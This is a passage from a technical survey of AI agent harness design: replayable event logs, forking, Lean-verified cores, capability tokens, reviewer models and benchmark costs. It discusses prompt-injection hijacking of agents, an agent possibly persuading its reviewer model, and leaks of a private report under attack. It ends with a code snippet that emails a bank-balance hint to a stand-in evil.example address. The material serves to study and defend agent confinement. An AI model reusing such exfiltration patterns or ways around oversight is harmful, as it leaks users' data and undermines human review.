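| Can a new run continue from here? | 160,076 | 120,969 | 36,251 |
| Is the world as if the later events had never happened? | 150,230 | 24,172 | 142,894 |

The 36,251 cuts in the second row separate a model request from its reply. In 24 of them, the run had failed and there was no reply. The 120,969 conditional cuts come after at least one completed model request, so the new run must use the recorded reply instead of calling the model again. All 160,076 unconditional cuts come before the first model request. The last row is stricter because a model call costs money, which can't be recovered by discarding the call's record.

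The first row is unsurprising for a pure fold. The other figures mostly reflect where model calls occur in these logs, so they don't predict how often real forks fail. They also depend on a list of event types that count as outside effects, so an unlisted type that had such an effect would be wrongly classed as harmless.

### Forking a run

A fork copies the start of a log and continues separately, for example to try another fix without repeating the earlier steps. ActiveGraph's forks reuse the recorded replies, so a fork at step 150 of a 200-step run needs new replies only for the steps from there on.

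The Synthetic Players data contains 121 real forks. Nakajima compared 16,625 copied events with the originals and found no differences in content or order. However, none of the copied parts contained a model call or any other outside request, so the data can't show whether forking is safe after such a request. To test that case, Nakajima built a single offline fork that inherits a recorded reply from a stand-in model. A counter confirmed that the fork made no second call. The test shows that the mechanism works, but not how it performs with a real provider.

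Copying the log also doesn't copy files or other external state. Suppose the user lets the bug fix finish, then forks the run from the point where the edit was waiting for approval. In the fork's log, `cart.py` still contains `sum(prices, 1)`, but the original run has already changed the file. If the user approves the edit in the fork, the tool won't find the text it is supposed to replace. Anthropic's documentation on agent sessions warns that forking a session copies the conversation but not the files, and that the fork's edits are visible to any session working in the same directory.

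A safe fork therefore needs a matching copy of the files and a fork point that doesn't fall between a request and its result. The *session fork* proposal (2025) for Agent Client Protocol, which connects editors to agents, has agents announce the positions at which they support a fork. An agent could leave out the unsafe ones.

### When the order of events matters

Replaying a finished log is deterministic, but that doesn't guarantee that the agent would produce the same log if run again, or that the run would end. Nakajima gives small counterexamples for systems like ActiveGraph, where one behaviour's output can trigger another.

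The first has a single behaviour, which reacts to the signal `loop` by emitting `loop`. It never stops, so it reached every step limit Nakajima tried, from 1 to 100. In a practical version from a workshop on agent harnesses, two plugins can keep responding to each other forever (AI Engineer, 2026). One possible remedy is to give every event a rank that must fall with each reaction. Fuel in the worked example follows the same principle.

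Another counterexample has two behaviours that write different values to the same place, so the last one wins. An obvious fix is to require that no two behaviours write to the same place, but a third example shows that this isn't enough:

- `left` and `right` both react to the start signal. They emit `left-ready` and `right-ready`, and write nothing.
- An observer reacts to `left-ready`. It writes 1 if `right-ready` has already arrived, and 0 if it hasn't.

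Only the observer writes anything, so there is no conflict between writers. But the result is still 0 if ActiveGraph processes `left-ready` first and 1 if it processes `right-ready` first. To rule this out, a check would have to cover what each behaviour reads, what it emits and what triggers it, as well as what it writes.

ActiveGraph handles events in the order they arrive and runs behaviours in the order the developer registered them. Repeated runs therefore usually agree, and ordinary tests don't reveal whether a behaviour's result depends on that order. Such a dependence could appear later, when a developer runs behaviours in parallel or changes the database. Nakajima didn't have a full list of the behaviours in production use, so nobody knows whether any of them depend on order.

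In the worked example, one `step` function handles every event from a single queue, so there is no choice of which handler runs first, and the log preserves the order in which outside events arrived.

### Pure decisions or only stored events

Many agent systems now keep an event log, but fewer make their decisions in pure code.

*Event-based Design Abstractions for Agent Harnesses* (Becker, Ghavami and colleagues, 2026), a workshop talk at the programming-languages conference PLDI, divides a harness into "facets", such as one for budgets and one for context. Each facet computes its own state by a pure fold over the shared log, has a rule for admitting new events, and can propose further events when its state changes. In *ESAA* (dos Santos Filho, 2026), models propose file changes as structured data, and a deterministic program validates, records and applies them. *The OpenHands Software Agent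 SDK* (Wang, Rosenberg and colleagues, 2026) describes a software-engineering toolkit that saves each event in a separate file.

| System | How it restores the state | Are the decisions pure? |
|---|---|---|
| Worked example | folds `step` over the events | yes, and Lean's types enforce it |
| Facets | each facet folds the shared log | the folds are; the design is in Python, which doesn't enforce it |
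| Temporal | reruns the workflow code against the recorded history | they must be deterministic, by rule |
| ActiveGraph | folds the log into a graph | no, behaviours call models and tools themselves |
| ESAA | computes a task list from the log | validation is deterministic, but the same program writes the files |
| OpenHands | loads a saved state file and the events | no, the agent loop calls the model and runs the tools |

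Among widely used systems, Temporal comes closest to the worked example. It separates workflows, which contain the decision logic, from activities, which perform effects. Temporal's *Workflow Determinism* requires a workflow to issue the same commands whenever it receives the same history. But a workflow is ordinary code, and its state includes the point the code has reached. Invariants about that point are harder to write than invariants about an explicit `State`. Temporal now has its own agent harness, in which tool calls and waits for approval survive a crash, and developers can supply their own agent loop.

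ActiveGraph forbids behaviours from reading the clock or generating random numbers directly, but doesn't enforce the rule in advance. In strict mode, a replay runs the behaviours again and stops at the first event that differs from the log. By default, if a developer edits a prompt and the new request doesn't match a recorded one, ActiveGraph makes a fresh call. It looks up recorded tool results by the tool's name and arguments. A test run before an edit and one after it can have the same name and arguments but different results, so a system like this also needs a rule for repeated calls. The worked example doesn't have this problem because each result has a call id and a place in the log.

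ESAA's description is inconsistent about when events are recorded. Dos Santos Filho writes that the system records an event before any irreversible effect, but the listed steps write files first and then append the events. If the files are written first, a crash can leave a changed file with no record of the change. The replay check wouldn't find this, because it compares the task list with the log and doesn't look at the source files. The evidence comes from only two trials. One completed 9 tasks with 49 events, and the other had finished 31 of 50 tasks when the paper was written. Every model proposal passed validation, so the trials don't show what happens when one fails.

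According to its *Persistence* page, OpenHands keeps settings, status and usage figures outside the log, in `base_state.json`, which it overwrites at every change. The log alone therefore can't reproduce the whole state, and a crash between writing to one and writing to the other could leave them inconsistent. On recovery, OpenHands looks for tool calls without a recorded result, like call 3 in the worked example.

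In its measurements, keeping a log took very little time or storage. Wang, Rosenberg and colleagues replayed 39,870 events from 433 programming conversations. Saving an event took a median of 0.2 milliseconds, while a model call typically takes 1 to 30 seconds. Recovery after a crash took a median of 7.4 milliseconds, and 32.1 milliseconds for the longest conversation, which had 358 events. The paper's text gives a figure under 20 milliseconds, which matches only the time for replaying the events. The median conversation took up 380 kilobytes.

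The redesigned OpenHands also had 61% fewer failures of its own than the old version when both served users for 15 days. The log probably explains little of the drop, because most of the failures that disappeared were network and login errors between two parts of the old system that the new version runs together.

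## What does a full agent runtime built this way in Lean prove and cost?

L3M, which Eisenach and colleagues at Amazon described in autumn 2026, is the fullest example of this design so far. It runs many agents at once, keeps all their state in Git, and lets them write their own tools. Like the worked example, it is written in Lean.

L3M separates decisions from effects in two places. Its event loop is a pure core with a shell around it, and Lean's types limit the effects that code inside its tools can have. The worked example left its tools unrestricted.

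### The event loop

Sources outside the loop post signals, for example when a model call returns or another agent sends a message. A single sequencer puts them into one ordered log. Leaving aside the review described below, a test run would go like this:

1. The model's reply arrives as a signal, and the sequencer records it.
2. A pure function folds the log into a state and computes what the agent owes next, which is a test run.
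3. The sequencer stores the new records in Git.
4. Only then does the shell start the test run. The result comes back as another signal.

Git also protects against a shell reusing an old state and starting the same tool twice, which `step` can't prevent. In L3M, a process can extend a log only if the log still ends where the process last read it. A second process with an out-of-date copy gets a conflict.

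Eisenach and colleagues proved three theorems about the order of events:

- `start_once`: the loop never starts the same activity twice.
- `open_call_is_last_call`: if a call has no recorded result, it is the last call in the log.
- `boot_close_eq_interrupt_close`: an agent that restarts with an open call closes it exactly as it would after an interrupt.

If L3M crashes during the test run, the restarted agent has only that one call to close, by `open_call_is_last_call`, and it needs no separate rule to close it, by `boot_close_eq_interrupt_close`. In the worked example, a programmer had to keep the `Interrupted` and `Restarted` branches consistent. The theorems cover only the sequencer and its records, so they can't show whether the tests ran before the crash.

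### What a tool's code can do

The proofs about the worked example cover the command `RunTool 2` but not the code that runs it. That code has the type `IO`, so an edit tool could also send the file to a stranger. Only the faithful-shell assumption rules this out. L3M needs to assume less because it restricts the tool's own code.

A tool in L3M can reach the outside world only through effect classes, which are named groups of operations such as reading files or using the network. Each operation requires a capability token, a value that lists what the operation may access. Tool code can't create these tokens. Here is a simplified version of the web-fetch tool.

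```lean
structure NetCap where
  private mk ::                -- other modules can't create one
  hosts : List String

class NetEffects (m : Type → Type) where
  fetch : NetCap → Url → m Response

def webFetch [Monad m] [NetEffects m] (cap : NetCap) (url : Url) :
    m (Option Response) :=
  if url.host ∈ cap.hosts then some <$> NetEffects.fetch cap url
  else pure none               -- refused, no request made
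```

`m` stands for an unknown kind of effectful program. Because `webFetch` must work for every `m`, its code can't use `IO` operations such as deleting a file. It can use only the operations of the classes in its type, which here means `fetch`.

A private constructor alone would leave loopholes, such as native code that builds a token outside Lean's checks. Every build of L3M therefore runs a linter on the code after Lean has resolved all names and abbreviations, so the linter catches forbidden calls made through an alias. It rejects any token created outside the token's own module. It also rejects file writes and process starts outside a short list of modules allowed to access the operating system, so a tool that calls Lean's ordinary function for writing files doesn't compile.

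*Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (2026) applies the same idea in Scala 3, whose compiler already tracks capabilities in types.

Suppose the agent that is fixing `cart.py` wants to look something up in Python's documentation. The fetch passes through these stages:

1. The user writes a grant, a record of what the agent may do. It allows network access to `docs.python.org`.
2. When the agent starts, L3M creates a token for each permission in the grant. The network token lists that one host.
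3. L3M offers the model only the tools that the tokens cover. Without network permission, the web-fetch tool would be missing from the model's list.
4. The model calls the tool with an address, and the tool's code compares the host with the token.
5. The tool calls `fetch`. The provider, which is the part of the shell that implements the effect class, checks the host again and makes the request.

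Eisenach and colleagues assume that an attacker can take over the model completely, for example through instructions hidden in a web page. If the hijacked model then requests `attacker.example`, L3M blocks the request. The model can still send any information it has to a permitted host. The theorem about hosts also assumes that the grant lists the permitted hosts, so it offers no protection if the user has allowed every host.

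An L3M tool calls `fetch` in the middle of its code and can use the response to decide what to do next, unlike a core that returns commands as data. The programmer can write ordinary sequential code, but can no longer test the tool by inspecting a returned list of commands.

The event loop determines when a tool starts, and the effect classes limit what the tool can do once it starts.

### Which calls need a review

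The worked example prompts the user about every edit and test run. L3M instead checks whether it could undo the action and whether a token limits the action's reach. If either is true, the tool is "tame" and runs without review. Otherwise, the tool is "wild", and L3M reviews every call by default. A tool that uses several effect classes gets the rating of the least reversible one, unless tokens limit all of them.

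| Action | Can L3M undo it? | Does a token limit it? | Review by default |
|---|---|---|---|
| Read `cart.py` | nothing to undo | yes, to the agent's directories | no |
| Edit `cart.py` | yes | yes, to the agent's directories | no |
| Fetch a web page | no | yes, to named hosts | no |
| Push a branch | no | yes, to named repositories | no |
| Run `pytest` in a Unix shell | no | no | yes |

A tame action can still do irreversible harm. For example, L3M doesn't review a push to a permitted repository, even if the agent has copied a password into one of the files. Eisenach and colleagues consider the push approved in advance because the user named the repository.

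The reviewer, usually another model, reads the call and the agent's stated reason, and judges the call safe or wild. The agent may keep the call, switch to a tame tool or withdraw. If it keeps a call judged wild, it sends a defence, and the reviewer judges once more. L3M asks the user only if the two still disagree. In unattended sessions, L3M instead follows a setting chosen in advance, which is to reject by default.

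Eisenach and colleagues motivate their work by citing a finding that users approve about 93% of Claude Code's permission prompts. They conclude that asking users to approve every call isn't real oversight.

The theorem `run_needs_safe_or_yes` establishes that a reviewed call runs only after a "safe" verdict that the agent accepted, or after the user's approval of a disputed call. Other theorems establish that every exchange ends and that a missing verdict counts as "wild". `run_needs_safe_or_yes` is weaker than `run_ok`, which requires the user's own approval of the exact call. A reviewer model can be wrong, and the agent's stated reason can leave out where a value came from, so Eisenach and colleagues treat review as an extra precaution and rely on the tokens to confine the agent.

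A user can avoid the review of test runs by approving a Makefile, a file of build and test instructions. L3M records hashes of the Makefile, the files it includes and the scripts it calls, and runs the Makefile only while all of these are unchanged. As described, this check doesn't cover the project's ordinary source files, so the tests would run whatever code `cart.py` contains at the time.

### Grants and fuel for child agents

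An L3M agent can start child agents. The child asks for a grant, and L3M refuses if the requested grant exceeds the parent's. The theorem `grant_restrict_le` shows that the basic operation, restricting a parent's grant, never produces a permission that the parent lacked.

It is harder to prove the same about a whole family of agents. Eisenach and colleagues proved that a descendant's grant can extend beyond the first agent's grant after only one generation, because a parent may give a child access to the parent's own Git branches, which the parent's stored grant doesn't list. The correct theorem limits each descendant to the first agent's grant plus each ancestor's own branches and mailboxes. It covers every sequence of grants that agents can issue, but stops applying once the user issues a new grant.

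The corrected theorem also doesn't guarantee that a child has no more permissions than its parent. A grandparent may later give the child a permission directly, and L3M then compares the new grant with the grandparent's permissions. A parent that starts a child without network access therefore can't rely on the child staying offline.

Fuel in L3M counts model calls, and a parent lends part of its own to each child. For one batch of loans, the theorem is:

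```
sum of the children's limits + what the parent has left ≤ the parent's limit
```

Suppose a parent with a limit of 100 has used 20 calls, and lends 30 to one child and 40 to another. It has 10 left. The total still available to the parent and children is 30 + 40 + 10 = 80, which is below 100. The theorem covers a single batch, whereas `at_most_five` in the worked example covers the whole run. Extending the theorem to a whole run would require an invariant that also accounts for later loans, returned fuel and changes to the budget.

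### Undo and its assumption about Git

L3M lets agents edit files freely because it can restore them. Before a tool writes to a file such as `cart.py`, L3M saves the old contents in Git. To rewind to an earlier turn, it restores every file changed since then from the saved copies and resets the agent's branches.

This works only if Git returns what it stored, and Git is a large C program that nobody has verified in Lean. Eisenach and colleagues therefore write the assumption down as a Lean proposition, with a description of what would show it to be false. Any theorem that needs it must take it as a premise. In outline:

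```lean
theorem undo_restores (git : ReturnsWhatItStored) (old : Bytes) :
    readBack (save old) = old
```

The premise has the same role as `Faithful` in `world_ok`, but it covers only one component. A developer can read the theorem's type to see what to test. If Git turned out to lose data, the developer could also see which theorems no longer applied.

A second theorem does the same for commits, assuming that Git's reset command restores a branch. Each undoable effect class also needs a proof that, in a mathematical description of its operation, undoing an action restores the previous state. In the proof for a file write, the undo checks that the file still has the new contents and fails if something else has changed them.

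The guarantee is temporary because Git eventually deletes old data that nothing refers to, including the saved copies. L3M also can't undo a push, a web request or the effects of a program that has already run.

### Tools that agents write

To collect every TODO comment in a project, an agent in L3M can write a small Lean program that reads all the files and returns a summary. Otherwise, it could read the files one at a time, with a model call for each. Saving the program is an ordinary edit and needs no review. The program becomes a new tool the next time the agent starts.

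The program's permissions are part of its type. The model that writes the program lists the effect classes the program uses, and Lean makes only those available to its code. If the list contains only file reading, a program that tries to fetch a web page doesn't compile. L3M then checks that the agent's tokens cover the list. A program can never do more than the agent could already do with its own tools, and it is subject to the same review rules as any other tool. The TODO collector only reads files, so it runs without review.

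L3M also has to prevent the source file from causing harm while Lean processes it. It accepts only a single expression and excludes tactics, which are small proof-building programs that Lean runs during compilation. It rejects unsafe or native code, any attempt to create a token, and any axiom beyond Lean's standard three.

A loaded program can start child agents within the agent's own grant. It can't call the model directly, build software, use a Unix shell or wait for an outside condition, so longer workflows that need these still have to go through the model.

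### What remains unproved

Eisenach and colleagues list the gaps in detail. The largest is that most of L3M's theorems are about individual checks, and no theorem combines them into a statement about a whole session. They argue in prose instead that the checks fit together. The small worked example goes further than L3M on this point, because `world_ok` connects every run of the core to what happens in the world.

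In L3M, keeping an agent's file access inside its directory depends on a theorem, C code and the operating system all being correct. The theorem establishes that the type used for paths can't express climbing out of the directory with `..`. A symbolic link (a file that redirects to another location) inside the directory could still lead to the system's configuration, so the C code that opens files refuses to follow such links. Even then, an agent can read an outside file through a hard link, a second name for the same file, if one already existed in its directory.

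A second gap is that the proof about undo covers only a mathematical model of a file write, and nothing proves that the provider's real write matches the model. For effect classes that only read, the evidence is weaker still, because L3M stores the names of the relevant checks and assumptions but no proof. These gaps can affect review, because L3M uses each class's declared rating to choose which calls to review.

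A third problem is loading source code written by a hostile model. According to The Lean Language Reference's *Validating a Lean Proof*, building source from a determined attacker can compromise the whole machine, since code that runs during the build can do anything. The manual recommends building such source in a sandbox and checking the exported proof outside it. L3M checks the form of an agent's program before Lean can run any code from it, but only tests and an informal argument support the claim that this stops every malicious file.

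The trusted base contains Lean's proof checker and compiler, six small C files that make the system calls, Linux, programs such as Git, and the model provider's interface. It also includes the user, who may write a grant that is too broad. If the user allows the unsandboxed Unix shell, none of the confinement applies to the shell.

The theorems also don't cover secrecy. To limit leaks, Eisenach and colleagues suggest splitting a research task between two agents that communicate only by messages. One can read the private source code but has no network access, while the other has network access but can't read the code. If the first agent's messages always total exactly k bytes, and the agents have no other way to influence each other, then everything the second agent sends out can reveal at most 8k bits about the code.

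This limit protects a large code base better than it protects a password. A 200-byte question may carry 1,600 bits, more than enough for a key. The agents could also pass information through the timing or number of messages. L3M doesn't yet enforce the limit, and a more detailed scheme, which labels data and counts how much of each kind an agent has read, exists only as a design.

The same split can keep hostile instructions away from the main agent. A program gives a web page to a child agent with no permissions, and accepts only "yes", "no" or "unclear" as its answer. A malicious page can then make the answer wrong, but it can't pass on any instructions.

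### What the restrictions cost

Eisenach and colleagues tested L3M on 37 tasks from Terminal-Bench 4.0.0, with three attempts at each. Each task provides a container and a written instruction, and its own tests grade the result. All the setups used Claude Opus 5 with a 75-minute deadline. In the table, pass@3 is the share of tasks solved in at least one of the three attempts. The other columns are averages over successful attempts.

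| Setup | Pass@3 | Model calls | Tokens (millions) | Minutes |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Code, permission checks off | 59.5% | 53.0 | 4.43 | 24.6 |
| L3M with a Unix shell, no review | 41.7% | 53.2 | 7.70 | 25.4 |
| L3M with a Unix shell, review, disputed calls approved | 40.5% | 100.9 | 12.10 | 30.4 |
| L3M with a Unix shell, review, disputed calls rejected | 43.2% | 107.3 | 12.81 | 28.1 |
| L3M with tame tools only | 27.0% | 53.3 | 7.74 | 21.6 |
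| L3M with tame tools, no agent-written programs | 24.3% | 41.5 | 6.17 | 24.5 |

The comparison between L3M with and without a Unix shell is the most informative, because the rest of the harness is the same. Eisenach and colleagues report that L3M scores about two thirds as high with tame tools as with the shell (27.0 against 41.7). Counted by individual attempts, the fraction is just over half, with 18 successes against 34.

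The sample is also small. The 27.0% is 10 of 37 tasks. No whole number of tasks out of 37 gives 41.7%, but 15 of 36 does, so one task may be missing from that result. Treating the two results as independent samples gives a 95% confidence interval for the loss of about –7 to 36 points. A task-by-task comparison would narrow the interval, but the true loss could still be much smaller or larger than 15 points.

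The loss also depends on the kind of task. Liu and Han (2026), in *What Does a Harness Buy?*, removed the Unix shell from Claude Code and tested it with the same model, Claude Opus 5, on 45 hard tasks in repairing existing software. The number of solved tasks changed by at most one. An agent can often repair code by reading and editing files, while many Terminal-Bench tasks require it to install or run something.

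The result rose from 9 tasks to 10 with agent-written programs. That difference could easily be chance, although five of the 18 successful attempts with tame tools used such programs. Anthropic's *Quantifying infrastructure noise in agentic coding evals* (2026) recommends scepticism about leaderboard differences below three points unless the test configurations are known to match. In Anthropic's tests, changing only the computing resources moved scores on an earlier Terminal-Bench version by six points.

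Review had no clear effect on success, but it increased model calls by roughly 85% and tokens by roughly 50% across all attempts. Among successful attempts, model calls about doubled. L3M reviewed only calls to the Unix shell, which were about a quarter of all tool calls. Each review added about 2.6 model calls and typically 8.6 seconds. Some of the extra tokens went to the reviewer, Claude Sonnet 4.6, which is a cheaper model.

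| Outcome of a review | Share of reviewed calls |
|---|---|
| Judged safe in the end | about 90% |
| Agent switched to a tame tool | about 6% |
| Agent withdrew the call | about 2% |
| Still in dispute, so a user would decide | 2.4% |

With a user present, L3M would have prompted them about roughly one reviewed call in forty. That would save users a lot of attention if the reviewer catches the dangerous calls, but these tests can't show whether it does. The reviewer initially objected to about a third of the calls, and about nine in ten second rounds ended with a "safe" verdict. This could mean that the first objections were mistaken or that the agent is good at persuading the reviewer. Finding out would require tests that include calls known to be harmful.

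### Is L3M behind because nobody has tuned it?

With a Unix shell and no review, L3M's task success rate was 18 points lower than Claude Code's. Eisenach and colleagues attribute the gap to a lack of tuning, since nobody has optimised L3M's prompts, tool descriptions or handling of long conversations against a benchmark.

The token counts partly support this explanation. Claude Code and L3M made the same number of model calls per successful attempt, but L3M used about 145,000 tokens per call and Claude Code about 84,000. L3M used just as many with only tame tools, so the extra tokens come from how it builds the model's input, not from the limits on its tools. How it builds the input explains its higher token use better than its failures.

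Other studies show that a harness alone can cause a gap of this size. In *When Agents Fail* (2026), the model MiniMax M3 scored 18 points higher on Terminal-Bench 2 in one harness than in another. Liu and Han cite a harness that scored 19.1% with a minimal connection to a benchmark and 73.4% with a complete connection.

Their own results are less favourable to the explanation. They compared Claude Code with mini-SWE-agent, which gives the model a short prompt, a single tool for running commands, and no handling of long conversations. With Claude Opus 5.5, the two scored within about two points of each other on 391 software repair tasks. A harness can therefore lack most of this machinery and still score about as well, at least on that kind of task. If L3M loses 18 points through its harness, the cause is more likely to be something that actively hinders the model than missing machinery.

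Claude Code may also have done better because it was paired with a model from the same company. In *ShellBench* (2026), two models from other companies scored 8 and 9 points lower in Claude Code than their averages across five harnesses. But Liu and Han found at most a small advantage for Claude Code with Anthropic's own model.

The test conditions offer further explanations:

- Eisenach and colleagues chose tasks that Claude Code had finished in a median of an hour or less. This excludes tasks that are slow in Claude Code but might be quick in L3M, and keeps those for which the reverse is true.
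- Terminal-Bench 4.0 allows eight hours per task, and these runs had 75 minutes.
- Claude Code's Unix shell could reach the network. L3M's standard Unix-shell tool can't, so an agent using it would have trouble with tasks that involve downloading software. That part of the gap would be a cost of the restrictions, and tuning wouldn't remove it.
- Chance may account for some of it. With 45 tasks and one run of each harness, Liu and Han calculate that a standard test detects a 13-point difference only about half the time. Three attempts per task help, but L3M's test had fewer tasks.

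Poor tuning is a plausible explanation for part of the gap, but only a new test with a tuned L3M could confirm it.

None of the six setups measures the overhead of the pure core, because all five versions of L3M use the same event loop. The core probably adds little overhead while an agent runs. Lean checks the proofs when it builds the program, so they take no time afterwards, and in the OpenHands measurements described earlier, saving an event took far less time than a model call.

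## Where else can the line between proved code and effects be drawn?

The worked example and L3M both run their event loops in Lean. A developer whose agent already exists in Python may want to prove only the part that grants permissions. Agenra suits this case because it puts a compiled Lean program between the agent and its Python tools. LLMbda, a programming language for agents, takes the opposite approach and proves more. Its theorems cover the language's whole interpreter, including the point where it calls the model. A compiler can also do some of the checking if the model writes its actions as a program in a language such as Scala.

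### A Lean gatekeeper for Python tools

When an agent that uses Agenra proposes a tool call, Python forwards the call to a Lean process that runs throughout the task. Lean looks for a permission that covers the call. If it finds one, it records that the agent has used it and answers "allow". Python runs the tool only after receiving this answer, then reports the result to Lean. The core in this design approves or refuses calls that the agent proposes, whereas `step` returns commands. Python decides when to call the model and what to do after a refusal.

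Each permission has a quota, which is the number of times the agent may use it. Lean deducts each use from the quota before the tool runs and doesn't restore it if the tool fails, because a failed call may still have had its effect. Fuel in the worked example follows the same rule.

The main example in *Agenra* is an agent that reads a private report, extracts the public fields and sends them to Alice once. Alice's address isn't known at the start, so the policy names the directory lookup that supplies it. A web page with a supposed new address for Alice can't change where the report goes. If a repeated lookup returns a different address, Lean withdraws the permission to send for the rest of the task. Lean also labels each stored value as public or confidential, and both the user's and the application developers' permission lists must allow every call.

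### Why a wider permission can break a task

Developers often change permission lists, and a change that only adds permissions looks harmless. Suppose a task may delete A and B once each. Lean searches the list from the top and counts each deletion against the first matching permission with quota left. A developer then widens the first permission from "B" to "A or B".

| Deletions | Old list: (1) B, once; (2) A, once | New list: (1) A or B, once; (2) A, once |
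|---|---|---|
| A, then B | allowed; A uses 2 and B uses 1 | B refused, because A has used 1 |
| B, then A | allowed; B uses 1 and A uses 2 | allowed; B uses 1 and A uses 2 |
| A, then A | second deletion refused | allowed; A uses 1, then 2 |

The wider list blocks a legitimate task and lets the agent delete A twice. Ordinary checks can easily miss both problems, because any single deletion that the old list allowed is still allowed, and a developer who tests B followed by A sees the task succeed.

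A cleverer rule could use permission 2 for A and save permission 1 for B. The first task would then succeed, but the agent could still delete A twice. No rule can always choose well, because the choice comes before the next deletion is known. Suppose the permissions are "A or B" and "A or C", each for one use, and the agent deletes A. If the rule uses the first permission, a later deletion of B fails, and if it uses the second, a later deletion of C fails. *Agenra* takes this result from earlier work on digital licences and keeps the simple top-down search, so that developers can at least predict which permission a call will use.

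### Comparing the old and new ledgers

A ledger is a permission list together with the number of times the agent has used each entry. To prove that a revision preserves every workflow, Agenra looks for a relation R between the old ledger's counts and the new ledger's counts that satisfies two conditions:

```
R(start, start')

if R(u, v) and the old ledger can charge call e, which changes u to u',
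then the new ledger can charge e, which changes v to some v' with R(u', v')
```

Such a relation is called a simulation. By induction, the new ledger allows every sequence of calls that the old one allowed. The proof works like the invariant proofs for `step`, except that the preserved statement is about both ledgers.

The deletion example has no simulation. After the agent deletes A, the old ledger still has a permission for B, while the new one has only a permission for A, so only the old ledger can charge B next.

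A quota increase always has such a relation. Let R mean that every permission has at least as many uses left in the new ledger as in the old one. Suppose the old ledger charges permission 3 for a call. If the new ledger does too, both counts fall by one and R still holds. Otherwise, the new ledger charges an earlier permission, say permission 1. The old ledger skipped permission 1 because it had no uses left, so the count in the new ledger can fall by one without dropping below the count in the old ledger.

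Agenra recognises two more kinds of edit that always preserve workflows. One adds a permission at the end of the list, and the other swaps two neighbours that never match the same call. Python code searches for a way to build a revision from such edits, and Lean checks the result. If that fails, the Python code can propose a finite table of related counts, and Lean checks the two conditions for every row. A mistake in the Python search can therefore prevent a certificate from being issued, but it can't produce a false one. The proof also covers message texts that weren't listed in advance, because no permission depends on the text.

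*Agenra* tests 51 revisions, including all 24 orderings of a list of four permissions. A separately written program explored every possible sequence of calls and found that 21 revisions preserved all workflows and 30 lost at least one. Lean certified the 21 that preserved all workflows and none of the other 30. It certified 16 from the simple edits and five from tables of counts. A check took about a tenth of a second.

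These results show that the method isn't too strict for this set, but Agenra's developers wrote the revisions themselves, so real changes might pass less often. They also tried one change from an existing program, Dyad, an open-source app builder that raised its free quota from five messages to ten. Lean certified the increase, but Agenra's model leaves out Dyad's refunds for failed messages and its timed quota resets, so the certificate covers only successful messages within one quota period.

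Preserving workflows also doesn't guarantee safety. If a developer raises the quota for sending the report from one to two, every old workflow survives, but the agent can now send the report twice. Agenra can search for forbidden sequences by calling the same Lean functions with simulated tool results. For the report task, a search up to six events visited about 67,000 nodes in under a second, and a search up to eight visited 12.3 million in two and a half minutes, so the method is practical only for short workflows.

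### What Agenra takes on trust

The proof about revisions assumes that each call finishes before the next begins, which Agenra enforces with a lock. It also assumes that tools return the same results under the old and new lists.

The largest assumption concerns Python, which translates the policy, passes each call to Lean and runs the tool. It must run exactly the call that Lean allowed. Some agent frameworks let developers add a check as a callback, but Lean can't block a call if the framework logs the callback's refusal as an error and runs the tool anyway. The developers must also declare correctly what each tool does. In one test, they registered a batch tool with fewer effects than it had, and Agenra allowed an undeclared deletion.

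A policy can be incomplete even when Lean enforces it perfectly. The original policy for the report task allowed the agent to send Alice any public text, not only the fields from the report. When the developers replayed calls from their live tests, five calls with the wrong text passed. After they added a rule that the text must come from the tool that extracts the public fields, Lean rejected all five.

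The live tests give little reason to choose Agenra for blocking attacks alone. Under a fixed set of attacks, an unguarded agent with a Qwen model sent the private report in 15 of 20 runs. It never did with Agenra or with a guard that the developers wrote by hand. The agent completed only 5 of the 20 attacked tasks in all three setups. Agenra's advantage over the handwritten guard is that developers can check a policy change before they install it.

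### A language interpreter that takes the model as an argument

*AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) introduces the language LLMbda. An LLMbda program can send a prompt, receive the reply and run the reply as code. It can also copy the conversation for a side task and then discard the copy, or start again with an empty conversation. The agent loop is an LLMbda program. The interpreter is a Lean function, and the main theorem covers every program it can run, including code that the model writes while the program runs.

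`step` asks for a model reply by returning `AskModel`, and receives the reply later as an event. LLMbda's interpreter instead takes the source of replies as an argument, called an oracle. In simplified form:

```lean
def Oracle := Nat → List String → String    -- request number, conversation, reply

step : State × Event → State × List Command
eval : Oracle → Program → Result
```

Garby and colleagues compare an oracle to an answer book printed in advance, with an entry for every request number and every possible conversation. When the program needs a reply, `eval` looks up the entry and carries on. The request number lets the same conversation receive different replies at different times. `eval` is pure because the same program and the same book always give the same result. (It also takes a limit on the number of steps, since Lean needs to know that the function ends.)

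In a live run, the replies come over the network instead of from a book. Lean lets a programmer declare a constant whose definition proofs can't use, and attach compiled code to it. Here the constant has the type `Oracle`, and its code sends the conversation over the network and returns the text of the reply. In the proofs, the constant is one of the possible books, so theorems that hold for every book apply to it. An oracle can therefore replace the list of commands, because a theorem about `eval` covers every reply by covering every book, just as a theorem about `step` does by covering every sequence of events.

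Models give random replies, so Garby and colleagues also prove that, for every program, `eval` returns results with the probabilities given by the language's mathematical definition. Suppose a program prompts the model twice to flip a coin that lands heads with probability 0.3, and counts the heads. If every entry in the book is an independent draw with that probability, `eval` returns 2 with probability 0.09, 1 with probability 0.42 and 0 with probability 0.49. The theorem assumes that the chance of each reply depends only on the conversation, so a provider that switched to another model during a run would break the assumption.

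The oracle makes programs easier to write, because a loop can get a reply partway through and use it on the next line. But `eval` has no state between events that a harness could save, and no point at which it could receive an Escape press. A harness could still recover from a crash by recording the replies and using them as the book for a second run.

Tools fit this scheme less well than models. Asking a model a question changes nothing outside the program except the amount of money spent, so it can fairly be described as looking up an answer in a book. A tool changes files or moves money, and a theorem such as `at_most_five` needs a record of the actions a program requested. LLMbda represents tools as pure functions that take a simulated world and return a changed one. Its theorems therefore don't cover a real bank or file system, which Garby and colleagues acknowledge as a limitation.

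### Labels and noninterference

Every value in LLMbda has a label, which can be "secret", "untrusted", both or neither. A computed value gets the labels of everything it depends on, so the length of a secret password is also secret. Dependence can be indirect, as in this fragment:

```
if first_letter(password) == "h"
then fetch("a.example")
else fetch("b.example")
```

Neither address contains any part of the password, but the owner of `a.example` learns the password's first letter from the visit. To prevent this, the interpreter keeps a program-counter label for the current point in the program. Inside the branches this label is "secret", and the interpreter applies it to every value computed there, including the two addresses. If `fetch` accepts only public addresses, the run stops, but the developer of `fetch` has to include that check.

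Such tracking is easy to get wrong. CaMeL, an earlier defence that also labels data while a program runs, has a gap that Garby and colleagues demonstrate with a bank balance. In outline:

```python
tmp, rich = True, True
if balance > limit: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.example", "rich!")
```

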